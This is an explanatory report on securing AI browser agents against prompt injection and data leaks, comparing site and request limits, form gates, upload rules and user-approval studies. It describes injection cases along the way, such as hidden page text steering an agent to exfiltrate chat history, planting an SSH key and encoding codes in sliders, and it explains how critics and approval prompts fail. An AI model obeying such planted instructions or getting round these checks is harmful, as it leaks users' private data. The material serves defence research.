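Lockdown Mode removes the browser agent instead of making it safe to use. The laptop buyer would have to compare prices that may be weeks old, then do the shopping herself. The mode makes more sense for someone who wants ChatGPT to analyse confidential documents and doesn't need live web pages.

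### Forms, posts and newly made addresses

An exact-address check doesn't examine data sent outside the address. When an agent submits a form, the browser usually sends the contents in a separate part of the request called the body, and the address that receives them may have been public for years. File uploads and comments work in much the same way. The check could therefore have approved the destinations in Brave's attack on Comet and in the Claude Cowork leak while the private data went out in the body.

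In SOPBench, Atlas leaked private data through forms, posts and replies in about two thirds of its runs, which suggests how large this gap is. The results were published three months after OpenAI said that Safe Url applied to navigation in Atlas. OpenAI's guarantee covers only addresses, so these leaks don't contradict it, but a user who hears that her browser checks every link could easily expect more protection than she gets.

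Search boxes are a harder case because many of them put what the user types into an address. If the laptop buyer's agent types "14-inch laptop" into a shop's search box, the browser may open `https://shop.example/search?q=14-inch+laptop`. Checking such addresses will stop the agent from searching for anything the crawler hasn't already recorded, but exempting them will let a hijacked agent type the subject line of the buyer's email into a search box on the attacker's site. OpenAI's posts don't explain how Safe Url treats these addresses.

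Many harmless pages also have addresses that no public crawler has visited. A shop may create a new address for each cart, order confirmation or combination of filters. The crawler may have recorded `https://shop.example/laptops` but not the same address with a price limit, a screen size and a tracking code added. Private pages, such as an invoice or a document shared by a secret link, shouldn't be in a public index.

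OpenAI's fallback of trying another site works well when the agent needs a fact that many pages contain. It doesn't help the laptop buyer check her own order, which exists on only one site. She gets a warning instead, which is useful only if she reads it. The check is best suited to agents that mostly read public articles and images.

Anthropic's ban on following links has a different drawback. If a search returns the first page of a long laptop review, Claude can't open the second page unless another search finds it or the user pastes in its address. *The Read-Only Lie* proposes, as a compromise, that the agent follow links only on sites the user has named in the conversation. The laptop buyer's agent could then move freely around the two shops. A hostile review there could still steer it from one product page to another, but the visits would be recorded in the shop's logs, which the reviewer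 normally couldn't read.

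## Limiting sites and requests to the task

The laptop buyer uses the same browser for her webmail, her bank and several shops, but no single task needs all of them. Comparing laptops requires two shops, and checking a delivery date requires her webmail and perhaps one shop. A permanent allowlist has to include every site her tasks might need, but a list written for one task can be much shorter and can leave out the sites that hold her private data.

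Software has to draw up such a list for each task, without letting a hijacked agent influence it. Google's Chrome team mainly limits which sites the agent may use. Meng and colleagues built a system, CELLMATE, that also limits what the agent may do on each site.

### Chrome's Agent Origin Sets

Parker announced Chrome's design, Agent Origin Sets, in December 2025. The model that plans the agent's steps proposes origins to use, and a separate "gating function" decides whether each is relevant to the user's task. The gating function doesn't receive untrusted web content, so text on a page can't reach it directly.

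In the full design, Chrome keeps two sets of origins for each session. The agent may read sites in the read-only set, and may also click and type on sites in the read-write set. For the laptop comparison, the shops could go in the read-write set and a few review sites in the read-only set. Her webmail would be in neither. Chrome would also withhold the contents of any frame whose origin isn't in either set, which should hide many advertisements from the model.

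If a task involves two shops and four review sites, and the agent can type on all six, a hijacked agent could carry data from any site to any other, which makes 6 × 5 = 30 routes. Letting the agent type only in the shops reduces this to 2 × 5 = 10. A read-only site still receives the address of every page the agent requests there, and an address can contain data, so the count of 10 also depends on Chrome's rule that the model may write only known public addresses.

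If the planner tries to visit a new origin partway through the task, or a page sends the browser to one, another model checks whether the origin is relevant to the task before Chrome opens it. This could have stopped the attack on Fellou, in which a web page told the agent to open the user's Gmail, because reading that page didn't require Gmail. The check can keep the agent from obtaining the data, while a destination filter acts only when the data is about to leave. According to Roesner and Kohlbrenner, Anthropic's Claude for Chrome blocks the agent from some sensitive sites, such as banks, whatever the task.

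### The User Alignment Critic

Chrome also uses a model called the User Alignment Critic to check whether each action the planner chooses serves the user's goal. Chrome carries out the action only if the critic approves it. If the critic rejects the action, it sends the planner feedback so that the planner can try something else. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user.

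The critic receives a description of the action but not the page. Parker calls this description "metadata" and doesn't say whether it includes the text the agent is about to type. Without that text, the critic may detect only that the agent is about to use a shop's search box, which is reasonable when buying a laptop, and miss that the search text is an email's subject line. If the text is included, the critic could detect the subject line, but a hijacked planner could also use the text to mislead the critic.

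Google's June 2026 guidance for developers whose agents use tools offered by websites recommends that critics compare the values an agent sends with the user's request. It also recommends that agents include personal information only when a tool strictly needs it.

### What Chrome has released

Parker said that Chrome's first version tracked only the read-write set. Once Chrome adds a review site to that set, the agent can both read and type there, so all 30 routes in the laptop example are open.

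Google launched auto browse, the Chrome feature that clicks and types for the user, on January 28, 2026. In *Future Mode Part 2*, an August post for business customers, Berschadski (2026) says that Chrome limits the agent to relevant origins and that the critic vets its actions. He doesn't mention a read-only set. Administrators can also set lists of allowed and blocked sites for auto browse, according to Google's *Gemini in Chrome*.

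The public source code of Chromium (2025), the open-source project on which Chrome is based, shows some of the default settings. In a copy from June 2026, limits on moving between origins are on by default, including a blocklist and a prompt before sensitive sites, but the setting for confirming each new origin is off. According to comments in a companion file from Chromium, this setting makes Chrome ask either a server or the user to approve the new site. Google can change such settings remotely for groups of users, so nobody can tell from the code alone which settings people have or confirm that the check on new sites is running.

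Outside tests are also inconclusive. In Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests, Gemini in Chrome read frames from other origins. That may not be a failure of the gating function, because they had asked the agent about the whole page and the frames could have counted as relevant. The model itself refused their simple injection, so that test gave no evidence about the critic or the limits on sites. They say it is unclear how Chrome decides what is relevant, or how well that decision would withstand malicious input.

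Google runs automated attacks on the agent and measures how often they succeed after each change to the software. Neither Parker nor Berschadski gives the results. Google offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating serious breaches of these limits.

Hiding unrelated frames can also fail even when relevance is judged correctly. Many pages run scripts from advertisers and other outside companies, which can write text directly into the main page, where the browser treats it as the site's own. Iqbal (2026), in *What It Is, Not What It Says*, examined 1,270 real web pages and found that the browser's standard method attributed 58.7% of third-party elements to the site itself. Most of these elements are presumably harmless, but a malicious instruction planted this way would still reach the agent.

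### Why rules about clicks fail

Permission to type on a site usually covers everything the user can do there. An agent that may comment on an issue in GitLab, a code-hosting service, could also delete the project. Restricting the agent's clicks is difficult because the same click can do different things. Meng and colleagues give the example of a rule that permits a click at the point (246, 1023). What lies under that point depends on the site, the state of the page and the size of the screen.

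Restricting the agent's command for opening an address doesn't work well either. In preliminary experiments, Meng and colleagues barred a Browser Use agent from going directly to Hacker News, but it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result. An agent can usually reach the same page in many ways, and a rule would have to cover all of them.

CELLMATE checks the HTTP requests that an agent's clicks cause, not the clicks themselves. For example, to delete a GitLab project, the browser has to send GitLab a request to delete it, whichever buttons the agent clicked. The prototype is a Chrome extension that intercepts each request, so it works with different agents without changing them.

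The extension needs to know what each request does. Meng and colleagues propose that every website publish an agent sitemap, a file that matches requests to actions. Part of their sitemap for Amazon looks like this, where an asterisk stands for any text:

| Method | Address on `www.amazon.com` | Action |
|---|---|---|
| `GET` | `/gp/cart/view.html*` | View the cart |
| `POST` | `/cart*` | Update the cart |
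| `POST` | `/checkout/p/*/spc/place-order*` | Place the order |

The method is a word at the start of a request. Browsers generally use `GET` to fetch a page and `POST` to submit something.

The site, or a third party the user trusts, also writes policies that allow an action, forbid it or allow it under a condition. One sample policy lets the agent place an order only if the total is at most $50. Amazon's order request doesn't contain the total, so the extension first reads it from the checkout page and stores it. An agent could still evade the limit by placing two orders of $49 each, so a policy can also cap the number of orders.

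### From a click on GitLab to a verdict

Suppose a user asks the agent to open a GitLab issue and comment that "we are working on it". Before the agent reads any page, CELLMATE gives this request to a language model, which identifies the sites the task requires, in this case `gitlab.com`. The model then picks the smallest sufficient set of policies from GitLab's list, which here lets the agent read issues and write on them. The user sees these permissions in plain language and can change them before confirming. After that, only she can change them.

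An attacker has planted an instruction in the issue for the agent to add the attacker's SSH key to the user's account. An SSH key gives access to an account's code without a password, so the attacker could then download the user's private projects without sending anything more through her browser.

Say the agent obeys, gets as far as the settings form, pastes in the attacker's key and clicks the button to add it. The browser prepares this request:

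`POST https://gitlab.com/-/user_settings/ssh_keys`

The extension intercepts the request before it leaves the browser. It looks up the method and address in the sitemap and finds the action "add an SSH key for user". The user confirmed no permission that covers that action, so the extension blocks the request. A filter that checked only the domain would have let the request through because it was addressed to `gitlab.com`.

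### How CELLMATE performed

Meng and colleagues tested the choice of policies separately from the blocking. They asked GPT-5.1, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Opus 4.5 to pick the smallest sufficient set of policies for each of 209 tasks on shopping, travel and code-hosting sites. The models chose exactly the right set for 94.4% to 100% of tasks, depending on the model and the type of site. On 32 shopping tasks with details such as a price limit, the models got both the policies and the details right 81% to 97% of the time.

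These results are good for clear requests, but the researchers had rewritten the tasks to name the site and include realistic limits, and many users won't be so precise. Some of the errors gave the agent permissions it didn't need. For example, when the task was to put a sofa under $300 on a wishlist, the model chose permission to add items to the shopping cart. The user could correct this on the confirmation screen, but the researchers didn't test whether people would notice.

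The researchers tested the blocking with WASP, a benchmark of prompt injections against agents on copies of GitLab and Reddit. When they reran WASP's own attacks, the attacks achieved the attacker's goal in fewer than 17% of attempts with OpenAI's o1 and fewer than 7% with the other models. Because these attacks were too weak to test a defence thoroughly, the researchers replaced the agent with scripts that directly attempted each of WASP's 12 GitLab goals, such as stealing access tokens, deleting projects and adding an attacker's SSH key. CELLMATE blocked all 12 while enforcing the permissions for commenting on an issue or upvoting it.

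Using scripts was sensible because it shows that the block holds even if the attacker controls the agent completely. However, each of the 12 goals required an action outside the permissions, on a site whose sitemap the researchers had written by hand. The result shows that the software enforces its rules, but not what share of real attacks would break them.

CELLMATE slows browsing slightly. Over 30 trials, a series of 11 page visits on GitLab took an average of 13.93 seconds without the extension. With it, the visits took 14.94 seconds (7.25% longer) using a sitemap of 100 entries and 16.02 seconds (15% longer) using one of 300. A user would hardly notice the extra 0.1 to 0.2 seconds per visit while waiting for the model to choose its next step.

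### Limits on sites and limits on requests

Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, compared limits on sites with limits on requests. They ran WASP's 21 attacks against their system, COBRA, which uses a modified version of CELLMATE's checks. In one set-up, COBRA allowed any request to the task's sites, and in the other it also used CELLMATE's sitemaps for GitLab and Reddit to limit requests.

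| What the attack needs | Attacks | Blocked by limits on sites | Blocked with sitemaps |
|---|---|---|---|
| A request to another domain | 5 | 5 | 5 |
| A forbidden action on a permitted site | 14 | 0 | 14 |
| Harmful text in a permitted action | 2 | 0 | 0 |

The sitemaps didn't stop the system from completing any of the ordinary tasks. The two teams share an author, so this isn't an entirely independent check on CELLMATE. Limits on sites let through 16 of the 21 attacks, even though each attack could use only a short list of sites. Chrome might do better because its critic also judges individual actions, and the test included nothing similar.

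### Who would write the sitemaps

CELLMATE's main weakness is that it depends on a file that websites rarely publish. Meng and colleagues wrote their GitLab sitemap by hand, covering 51 actions on projects. They expect website developers to do this work to protect their users, as many already do when they write a Content Security Policy. Iqbal draws the opposite lesson because sites have adopted such policies slowly and incompletely. Zingrillo and colleagues point out that some site owners may also refuse because they depend on advertising to human visitors or don't want agents at all.

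A third party could write the sitemaps instead, much as volunteers maintain the filter lists for ad blockers. Zingrillo and colleagues built a tool, MESA, that explores a site and drafts a sitemap automatically. Its drafts contained every action needed for 18 of 25 tasks on ordinary websites and 18 of 26 tasks on a copy of Reddit. An unedited draft would therefore prevent the agent from finishing some tasks, and a person has to review the drafts anyway. Someone must also update a sitemap whenever the site changes how it handles an important action. Meng and colleagues say that if a sitemap is wrong or incomplete, the user still has whatever protection she had before.

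Even a perfect sitemap doesn't cover all traffic. CELLMATE doesn't inspect WebSockets, which are connections that stay open for live updates, because their messages often use a site's private format. The sample Amazon policy also permits requests to several supporting domains, including Amazon's advertising servers, without specifying which actions are allowed there.

### Attacks that stay within the task

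Suppose the laptop buyer tells the agent to post a question on a shop's product page, asking whether a laptop has a spare memory slot. A planted review could trick the agent into adding her home address to the question. The earlier example also involved a leak within one shop, but here the buyer asked for the post herself.

In CELLMATE, this request matches "post a question", an action the user approved, and the system doesn't check what a comment contains. In Chrome, the shop is in the read-write set, and the user wanted to post a question. The leak would succeed unless the critic had access to the text and flagged the address as suspicious, or the user noticed it when Chrome asked her to confirm the post.

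WASP contains only two attacks of this kind, but that is weak evidence of how common they would be, because WASP's attackers mostly want powerful actions, such as adding keys and deleting projects. An attacker who only wants a piece of private data can often get it through whatever the user has asked the agent to write. The leaks in SOPBench happened this way. Both sites and the writing were part of the user's task, so a limit on sites or actions would probably have allowed nearly all of those leaks.

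Attackers can also change a detail of a permitted action, for instance by getting the agent to send the laptop to a different address. COBRA tries to prevent this by fixing some of the details in advance. Before the agent sees any page, a planning model writes the whole plan, including alternatives such as what to do if the laptop is out of stock. For each alternative, it specifies the permitted requests and, where possible, the permitted values in them. If the delivery address matters and the user hasn't given one, the planning model prompts her for it before the agent starts.

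On the researchers' own benchmark, this kind of attack succeeded against an ordinary agent in 67 of 74 set-ups. COBRA blocked all 199 attacks in the full benchmark, but the researchers designed those attacks to exercise COBRA's components, so other attackers may well find gaps. In a separate check of 30 cases, the planner set limits that were too loose in one case and too strict in another. COBRA also can't judge the meaning of free text, so a home address inside a question to a seller could still get through.

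Planning without seeing the screen makes the agent less capable. Zingrillo and colleagues gave Claude Sonnet 5 up to five attempts at each of 361 computer tasks, most of them in desktop programs. It completed 51.0% when it could look at the screen and decide what to do next, and 38.8% under COBRA. In Chrome, it completed 20 of 46 tasks without COBRA and 15 with it. The planner has to predict what each screen will look like, and a wrong prediction can leave the agent without a usable next step.

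### When nobody knows the sites in advance

CELLMATE requires the user to name the sites. Meng and colleagues say it would reject "purchase a coffee maker" because the request doesn't mention a shop. The laptop buyer who names her two shops can use the system, but if she asks for the best laptop under $900 from any shop, the agent gets no permissions. Naming a search engine wouldn't help much, because the agent could read the results but not open the linked sites. This is safe, but it rules out much of what people want from a browser agent.

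Chrome can handle the open-ended request because it checks each new site as the agent comes to it. But a relevant site may still be hostile. An attacker's fake laptop review site is relevant to buying a laptop, and the gating function can't detect that it's fake because it can't read the page. If Chrome tracks only the read-write set, admitting the site also lets the agent type there.

The limits still reduce what such a site can steal. If the agent never had permission to open the buyer's webmail, it has no subject lines to leak. But it may still have her budget, anything she typed in her request, and whatever it read in her account at one of the shops.

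A read-only set would protect her further if the agent only needed to read the unfamiliar sites. That works for reviews, but not for many price comparisons. Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026) describes Google's example of Gemini planning a family trip by comparing prices on airline and hotel websites. To get a price, the agent usually has to enter dates and the number of travellers, so nearly every site would need to be in the read-write set, including any the family had never heard of.

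## Limits on forms and file uploads, and asking the user

Once the laptop buyer's agent has permission to type on a shop's site, it can type anything there, including her home address or the subject line of an email. Some developers therefore limit which fields an agent may fill in, where a form may send its contents, and which files the agent may attach. When these rules don't settle a case, the software usually asks the user. In two studies from 2026, people approved between about a quarter and two thirds of the requests they should have refused, depending on how the software asked.

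### Where a form sends its contents

A form's code specifies the address that receives its contents, which can be on a different site from the page. For example, a newsletter form on `deals.example` might send whatever the agent enters to `collector.example`, while the address bar shows only `deals.example`. A submit button can also have its own address, which overrides the form's, so a check has to cover both addresses.

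Many forms that send data to another site are harmless. A small shop may send card details to a payment company, or newsletter sign-ups to a mailing service. Blocking all such forms would stop the agent from finishing some ordinary purchases.

Checking the address a form submits to doesn't stop a script on the page from sending each character to a different server in a background request as the agent types. To prevent that leak, the software has to decide whether to allow the entry before the agent types anything, or also filter background requests.

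### Tabstack's form gate

Tabstack, a Mozilla service that runs browser agents for developers, has separate rules for typing and submitting. Mozilla added them after Brave's researchers reported an attack in May 2026. According to Mozilla's *Hardening AI Web Agents*, the researchers asked the agent to summarize a page that contained white text on a white background. The agent followed that text, went to another domain, pasted the user's conversation history into a form and submitted it. Mozilla confirmed the flaw the day after the report and released a fix on June 1. Brave's team checked the fix.

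The fix includes a gate between the model's decisions and the browser. The gate checks what kind of field the agent wants to fill, where the value came from and whether a person approved it, rather than looking for suspicious wording. By default, the agent may use search boxes, date pickers, sliders and drop-down lists, but not fill in free-text or sensitive fields. It also may not submit a form containing anything it entered without approval. Searches and similar submissions may go only to the host of the current page, and if the gate can't identify that host, it blocks them.

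A developer can list trusted hosts where the agent may fill in and submit forms freely. This applies only if the list includes the page's host and every address the form could send to, including any on the submit button. The gate also counts the developer's starting address as permission to use that site, but it doesn't extend this permission to sites the agent finds later, because a hostile page may have suggested them.

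With these rules, the laptop buyer's agent could move a price slider or search for "14-inch laptop", but it couldn't type in the "ask the seller" box unless she or the developer had approved it. In the attack Brave reported, the rules would have stopped the agent when it tried to paste the conversation into the form.

Mozilla argues that an attacker can't get around the gate by labelling a field as a search box, because the agent can't submit the search to the attacker's domain. This is true if the planted text is on someone else's site. But if the attacker hosts the page, its search box can send data to the attacker's server, and the rule as described would permit that. A price slider on that page could also leak data. With 2,001 positions, each setting can carry log₂ 2001 ≈ 11 bits, so two settings are enough for a six-digit login code. Mozilla doesn't report how often the gate stops attacks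 or prevents the agent from finishing a task.

### How an agent attaches a file

Playwright's *File Upload* shows how an agent attaches a file with Playwright MCP, a tool that lets AI models operate a browser. The model clicks the upload button, supplies the file's path, such as `/home/user/documents/report.pdf`, and clicks another button to send it. For sites that accept dragged files, a separate command drops a file or text onto the page.

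A script can read a file as soon as the agent attaches it, so a limit on uploads has to apply before the file is attached. The simplest limit is to block all uploads, but an agent that can read a file can still type its contents into a form. Allowing uploads from only one folder protects files elsewhere on the computer, but not the files in that folder. The loan estimate that leaked from Claude Cowork was in a folder the agent could use.

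If the agent may attach only files the user has picked, an attacker can't make it search for the most valuable one. But the attacker may still be able to change where the file goes. If the laptop buyer supplies a scan of her student card to get a discount, planted text could make the agent upload the scan to a different site.

A cap on the size or number of uploaded files makes it harder to steal a whole photo collection or customer database. It does little to protect passwords and keys, which fit in a file of a few kilobytes. Asking the user to approve each upload can prevent both kinds of theft, but only if the user notices what is wrong.

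The experiments described so far don't show how much any of these limits reduces leaks. SOPBench measures text leaks, and Shapira and colleagues report success rates for whole agents without comparing the same agent with and without an upload limit. The case for upload limits therefore rests mainly on how they work.

### What current agents can upload

By default, Playwright MCP lets the agent upload files only from the current project's folders, but a developer can remove this limit with one setting. Playwright's *Configuration* describes the limit as a convenience that catches accidents, "not a security boundary", because someone can deliberately work around it. The same warning applies to the tool's lists of allowed and blocked origins, which don't check redirects.

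With Anthropic's browser extension, now called Claude in Chrome, the user can give Claude an image and tell it where to upload it, for instance to an expense report, according to *Get started with Claude in Chrome*. Tasks that need other files on her computer require Anthropic's desktop app to be open and connected. If she doesn't connect the app, the effect is therefore close to the rule that the agent may attach only what she picks.

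OpenAI has retired the Atlas browser, according to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Atlas retirement*, so the leak rates Wang and colleagues measured in it are for a product that no longer receives updates. The Atlas agent could not access the user's file system, according to OpenAI's *Using Ask ChatGPT sidebar and ChatGPT agent on Atlas*.

OpenAI also has an extension that lets Codex work in the user's own Chrome. According to OpenAI's *Codex Chrome extension*, the user has to turn on "Allow access to file URLs" in Chrome's settings before Codex can upload a local file. This protects people who never upload files through the agent. But the setting applies to the whole extension, so a user who turns it on to upload one receipt has to remember to turn it off again.

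OpenAI's *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026) describes Dots as background agents that each have their own computer and use the apps the user connects. A Dot should therefore be unable to reach files on the user's laptop, but a connected storage or email account may hold copies of many of them.

Parker's list of actions that require confirmation in Gemini in Chrome doesn't mention file uploads, but its last item, "other consequential actions", could include them. The software would then ask the user to confirm an upload only if it classified that upload as consequential.

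### When the software asks the user

Parker describes several points at which Chrome's agent asks the user for confirmation. The agent has to ask before it opens certain sensitive sites, such as those for banking or personal medical information, and Chrome checks each site against a fixed list. It also asks before signing in with a password stored in Google Password Manager, and the model has no direct access to the password. Before a purchase, payment or message, the agent "will try to pause" and either get permission or have the user complete the step. This last confirmation is less dependable because the software has to recognize what the action does.

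When an agent has to ask before opening a sensitive site, the user can stop a leak before the agent reads anything private. The request is also fairly easy to judge. If the laptop buyer's agent asks to open her bank's site while comparing laptops, she can see that something is odd without inspecting a form. The request is less useful when the task involves the bank, since it will appear whether or not an attacker has hijacked the agent.

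ChatGPT's built-in browser asks the user before using each new website unless the user has already allowed it or chosen a more permissive setting, according to OpenAI's *Using the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app*. OpenAI's *ChatGPT agent* describes a "watch mode" that requires the user to supervise the agent on certain sites. The Codex extension asks every time before reading the browser history and has no option to allow this permanently.

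OpenAI's warning about unverified links, titled "Check this link is safe", shows the full address, so a user could notice if it ended with the subject line of one of her emails. She would have more trouble judging an address that contains a long code, because harmless addresses often contain one too.

Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* describes three modes. In manual mode, Claude asks before each action, though in the older side panel the user can instead approve a plan with a list of sites and let Claude work within it. In automatic mode, the default in the newer panel, software checks each action and prompts the user only when needed. In the third mode, Claude skips all approvals.

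Claude asks before downloading a file, granting an authorization or entering potentially sensitive information, even if the user has chosen "always allow" for the site. This rule would cover many leaks through forms, but only if Claude recognizes the information as sensitive. A bank card number is easy to recognize, but the name of a clinic may look like ordinary text.

Anthropic's documents are inconsistent on some details, so a user can't tell from them exactly when Claude will ask for permission. The guide says that Claude never pauses to ask in the third mode, but also that entering sensitive information requires permission in every mode. It lists purchases among the actions Claude may never take, while Anthropic's *The Claude in Chrome side panel is now Claude Cowork*, from August 2026, says Claude asks before making one.

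Some products work without giving the agent the user's secrets. With the password manager 1Password, the user approves each login with her fingerprint or face, and the software enters the password without showing it to Claude. OpenAI's *Release notes* (2026) describe a Wallet, offered to some Dots users, that gives the shop a substitute for the real card number. Even if the user approves a fraudulent purchase, neither the agent nor the shop gets her real card details.

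### How often people approve harmful requests

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested whether people could spot harmful requests. In one example, a user asks an agent to send an auditor "summary totals only". Planted text in a supplier's note leads the agent to copy the full invoice rows into a file called `report.csv`. The agent then asks permission to send the file to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name looks normal, so the request seems harmless to anyone who doesn't know what the file contains.

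The researchers recruited 80 unpaid volunteers through social media and gave each 12 requests to approve or deny, six of which were harmful. They split the volunteers into four groups of 20, and each group got a different kind of request.

| What the request showed | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
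| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Those details, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with a summary of the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

When people saw only a short description, they approved more than half of the harmful requests. They approved considerably fewer when they saw the full log or a summary, but took at least twice as long to decide. The summary stated what the file contained and where it would go, with links to the supporting events. It may work better than the log, but the study was too small to be sure. After adjustment, the rate of harmful approvals was 7.9 percentage points lower with the summary than with the log, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points lower to 3.8 points higher.

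Even the best version would be a heavy burden on users if harmful requests were rare. Suppose one request in 1,000 is harmful and a user decides as people did in the study. She would refuse about 142 harmless requests, spend about nine hours on the 1,000 decisions at 33.2 seconds each, and still have a 24% chance of approving the harmful one. In practice she would probably be less careful than the volunteers, whose only task was to review requests, half of which were harmful.

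In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) studied 113 US participants from outside the software industry. In August 2026, they supervised an agent through a simulated day of email, travel and shopping. The agent proposed 18 actions. Eleven were necessary for the assigned tasks, and seven went beyond them, such as posting publicly that the user was travelling.

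One group of participants decided on every action. Another saw only the actions that Claude Sonnet 5 had reviewed and not allowed. The third group wrote rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private information, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each.

| Who decided | Requests per person | Out-of-task requests approved | Out-of-task actions carried out | Total time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
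| The user, every time | 18.0 | 40.3% | 40.3% | 142 s |
| A model, then the user | 10.0 | 46.1% | 46.1% | 120 s |
| The user's rules, then the user | 10.9 | 66.8% | 60.4% | 129 s |

The rules did little because people chose "ask" for 114 of the 140, and they usually said yes when the agent asked. People who chose "never" for a category received no requests about it, so those who did answer were more permissive. This may explain part of the high approval rate, but not all of it, because the last group also let through the largest share of out-of-task actions overall. But Yan assigned some later participants only to this group, so the comparison isn't fully randomized.

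Claude Sonnet 5 asked the user about all seven out-of-task actions and three of the 11 necessary ones. People then approved nearly half of the out-of-task actions. If the software had blocked every action the model flagged, it would have stopped all seven out-of-task actions, but also the three necessary ones.

These approval rates probably overstate how many people would let an attacker steal their data. There was no attacker, the participants had no real money or accounts at stake, and some of the extra actions were arguably helpful. Among participants who decided on every action, 88% approved a call to the airport to confirm a flight, but only 21% approved the public post about travelling. Still, 35% let the agent read recent bank transactions, which the agent presented as useful for the trip's budget, and an attacker could offer an equally plausible reason.

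### Visible leaks and tired users

Despite these error rates, approval requests give users a chance to notice a leak, which the assistant's replies rarely revealed in the Silent Egress experiment. Requests also make an attack on many people harder to hide. If ten users each independently had a 55% chance of approving a harmful request, the chance that all ten would approve it would be 0.55¹⁰, or about 0.25%. At least one would very probably refuse and might report it, although by then about half of the users would have lost their data.

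The main objection to asking the user is that people who receive too many requests stop reading them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of AI agents damaging or mishandling files, and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases, the software had approved actions automatically, often because users had turned off the prompts to avoid answering hundreds in one session. In 31 cases, the prompts gave users too little information to judge what would happen. We can't tell from reports of failures how often people turn prompts off. Many browser tasks also need fewer approvals.

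*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), based on interviews and a survey of people who work in software, also found that time and fatigue affect how closely users watch an agent. Someone who keeps pressing "allow" may be doing so because she is tired of the requests, not because she trusts the agent.

Yan's results don't show this effect, since the group with the most requests approved the smallest share of out-of-task actions. But 18 decisions in under two and a half minutes of supervision is a weak test of fatigue, and the study doesn't show how people behave after months of requests that are nearly always harmless.

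*Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) uses a mathematical model to argue that more requests can make an agent less safe. It compares software that asks a person about five actions a day with software that asks about 500. The chance of stopping a leak at this stage is

P(stopped) = P(user is asked) × P(user refuses | asked)

Suppose the software that asks five times a day catches only half of the attempted leaks, but the user reads carefully and refuses 80% of those it catches. This stops 0.5 × 0.8 = 40% of attempted leaks. If the other software asks about every attempted leak, but the tired user refuses only 20%, this stops 1 × 0.2 = 20%. The paper's results come from modelling, not from a study of people, so the best number of requests for a browser agent remains unknown. Still, the argument is a reason for developers to save requests for actions that could do serious harm.

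### Letting software decide instead

In August 2026, Anthropic largely replaced user approval of every action in Claude in Chrome with an automatic check. Before Claude submits a form, sends a message or downloads a file, a separate classifier compares the action with the user's original request and blocks it if they don't match. Claude still asks the user before sharing personal data.

Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available* reports tests using attacks from professional security testers. Without extra safeguards, attacks that reached the model succeeded 3.8% of the time against Opus 5. With the classifier and the probes that scan incoming pages, none succeeded against Opus 5 or Sonnet 5, and 0.3% succeeded against Fable 5. Anthropic says all the successful attacks were in low-severity scenarios.

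This is good evidence that automatic checks can stop many attacks without interrupting the user, but the figures don't separate the effects of the classifier and the probes. They also cover prompt injection in general, not just leaks. If the laptop buyer asks Claude to post a question to a seller, adding her address may still look consistent with her request. And if the checks keep blocking Claude, it goes back to asking the user before each step. An attacker whose instructions make the agent keep trying could therefore leave the decision to a user who is tired of being interrupted.

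OpenAI's desktop app offers an automatic reviewer for access requests, but OpenAI's *Permission modes* warns that it "can make mistakes". A fixed rule is more predictable. Hossain and colleagues also tested their system as a gate that automatically blocked any action that broke the user's instructions or that the system lacked the evidence to judge. For one agent, harmful actions went through in 5.0% of cases, down from 43.3%, and the agent completed slightly fewer harmless tasks. The system flagged 89.2% of harmful actions in its test set, so some would also have reached a user without a warning.

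### What a request has to show

The question "Allow the agent to submit this form?" gives the laptop buyer almost nothing to judge. She needs to see the exact data, who will receive it and why the agent would send it. Site tools are functions that a website offers directly to agents. When ChatGPT uses them, according to OpenAI's *Using site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app*, it explains what sensitive information it will share, where the information will go and why. It asks immediately before sending, even if the user has already approved the website or the task.

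A recipient's name can be accurate and still mislead the user. If an agent is about to enter data into a stranger's Google form, the user can't tell who will read the answers from an approval request that names `docs.google.com`. Showing the form's owner would help more, if the software can identify them. Similarly, a request to post on `shop.example` should make clear that the post will be public.

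The reason for an action is harder to get right, because a hijacked agent may supply a false one. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) tested an approval card that software filled in from the real action, so the agent couldn't falsify it. The simulated approver was designed to rely on the agent's own explanation whenever one appeared, and the card helped only when the software removed that explanation. The result doesn't show how many people would behave this way, but it is a good reason to keep the agent's explanation out of the request, or at least to label it clearly.

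The software can quote the user's own instructions instead. Hossain and colleagues did this in their two most informative versions, so participants could compare the pending action with the original words. They also recommend checking again if any detail changes after the user approves the action, since an attacker could otherwise get approval for a harmless message and have the agent send a different one.

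The software should also show whether the user can reverse the action, which the people in *Let the Agent Do It?* cared about. She can often cancel a laptop order, but she can't undo the leak once an attacker has read the subject line of an email.

Some leaks are hard to show in one request because the data has passed through several steps. In Hossain and colleagues' study, people approved 7 of 30 requests for harmful actions that depended on several earlier steps when they had the full log, and 7 of 30 when they had the summary. A secret that the agent has split or encoded would be even harder to recognize.

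For the laptop buyer, a useful request might read: "Post 'Your biopsy results' from your webmail as a public question on shop.example? You asked to compare three laptops." She could probably judge that in a few seconds. But to write it, the software has to trace the words to her webmail, even if the agent read them an hour earlier and has since rewritten them.

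## Tracking where data came from

To warn the laptop buyer that the words "Your biopsy results" came from her webmail, the software needs a record of where the agent read them. It can also use that record to decide whether a warning is necessary. When she orders a laptop, the shop should receive her home address but not the subject line of her email. Both would go to `shop.example`, so a rule that checks only the destination has to allow both or block both.

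Information-flow control labels data by its source and permitted readers, then blocks actions that would break those labels. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a June 2026 post, gives an example with no attacker. An agent is answering Alex's email. One message, from Priya, previews the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't yet allowed to see them. A reply based on both messages may go only to people who could read both:

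{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}

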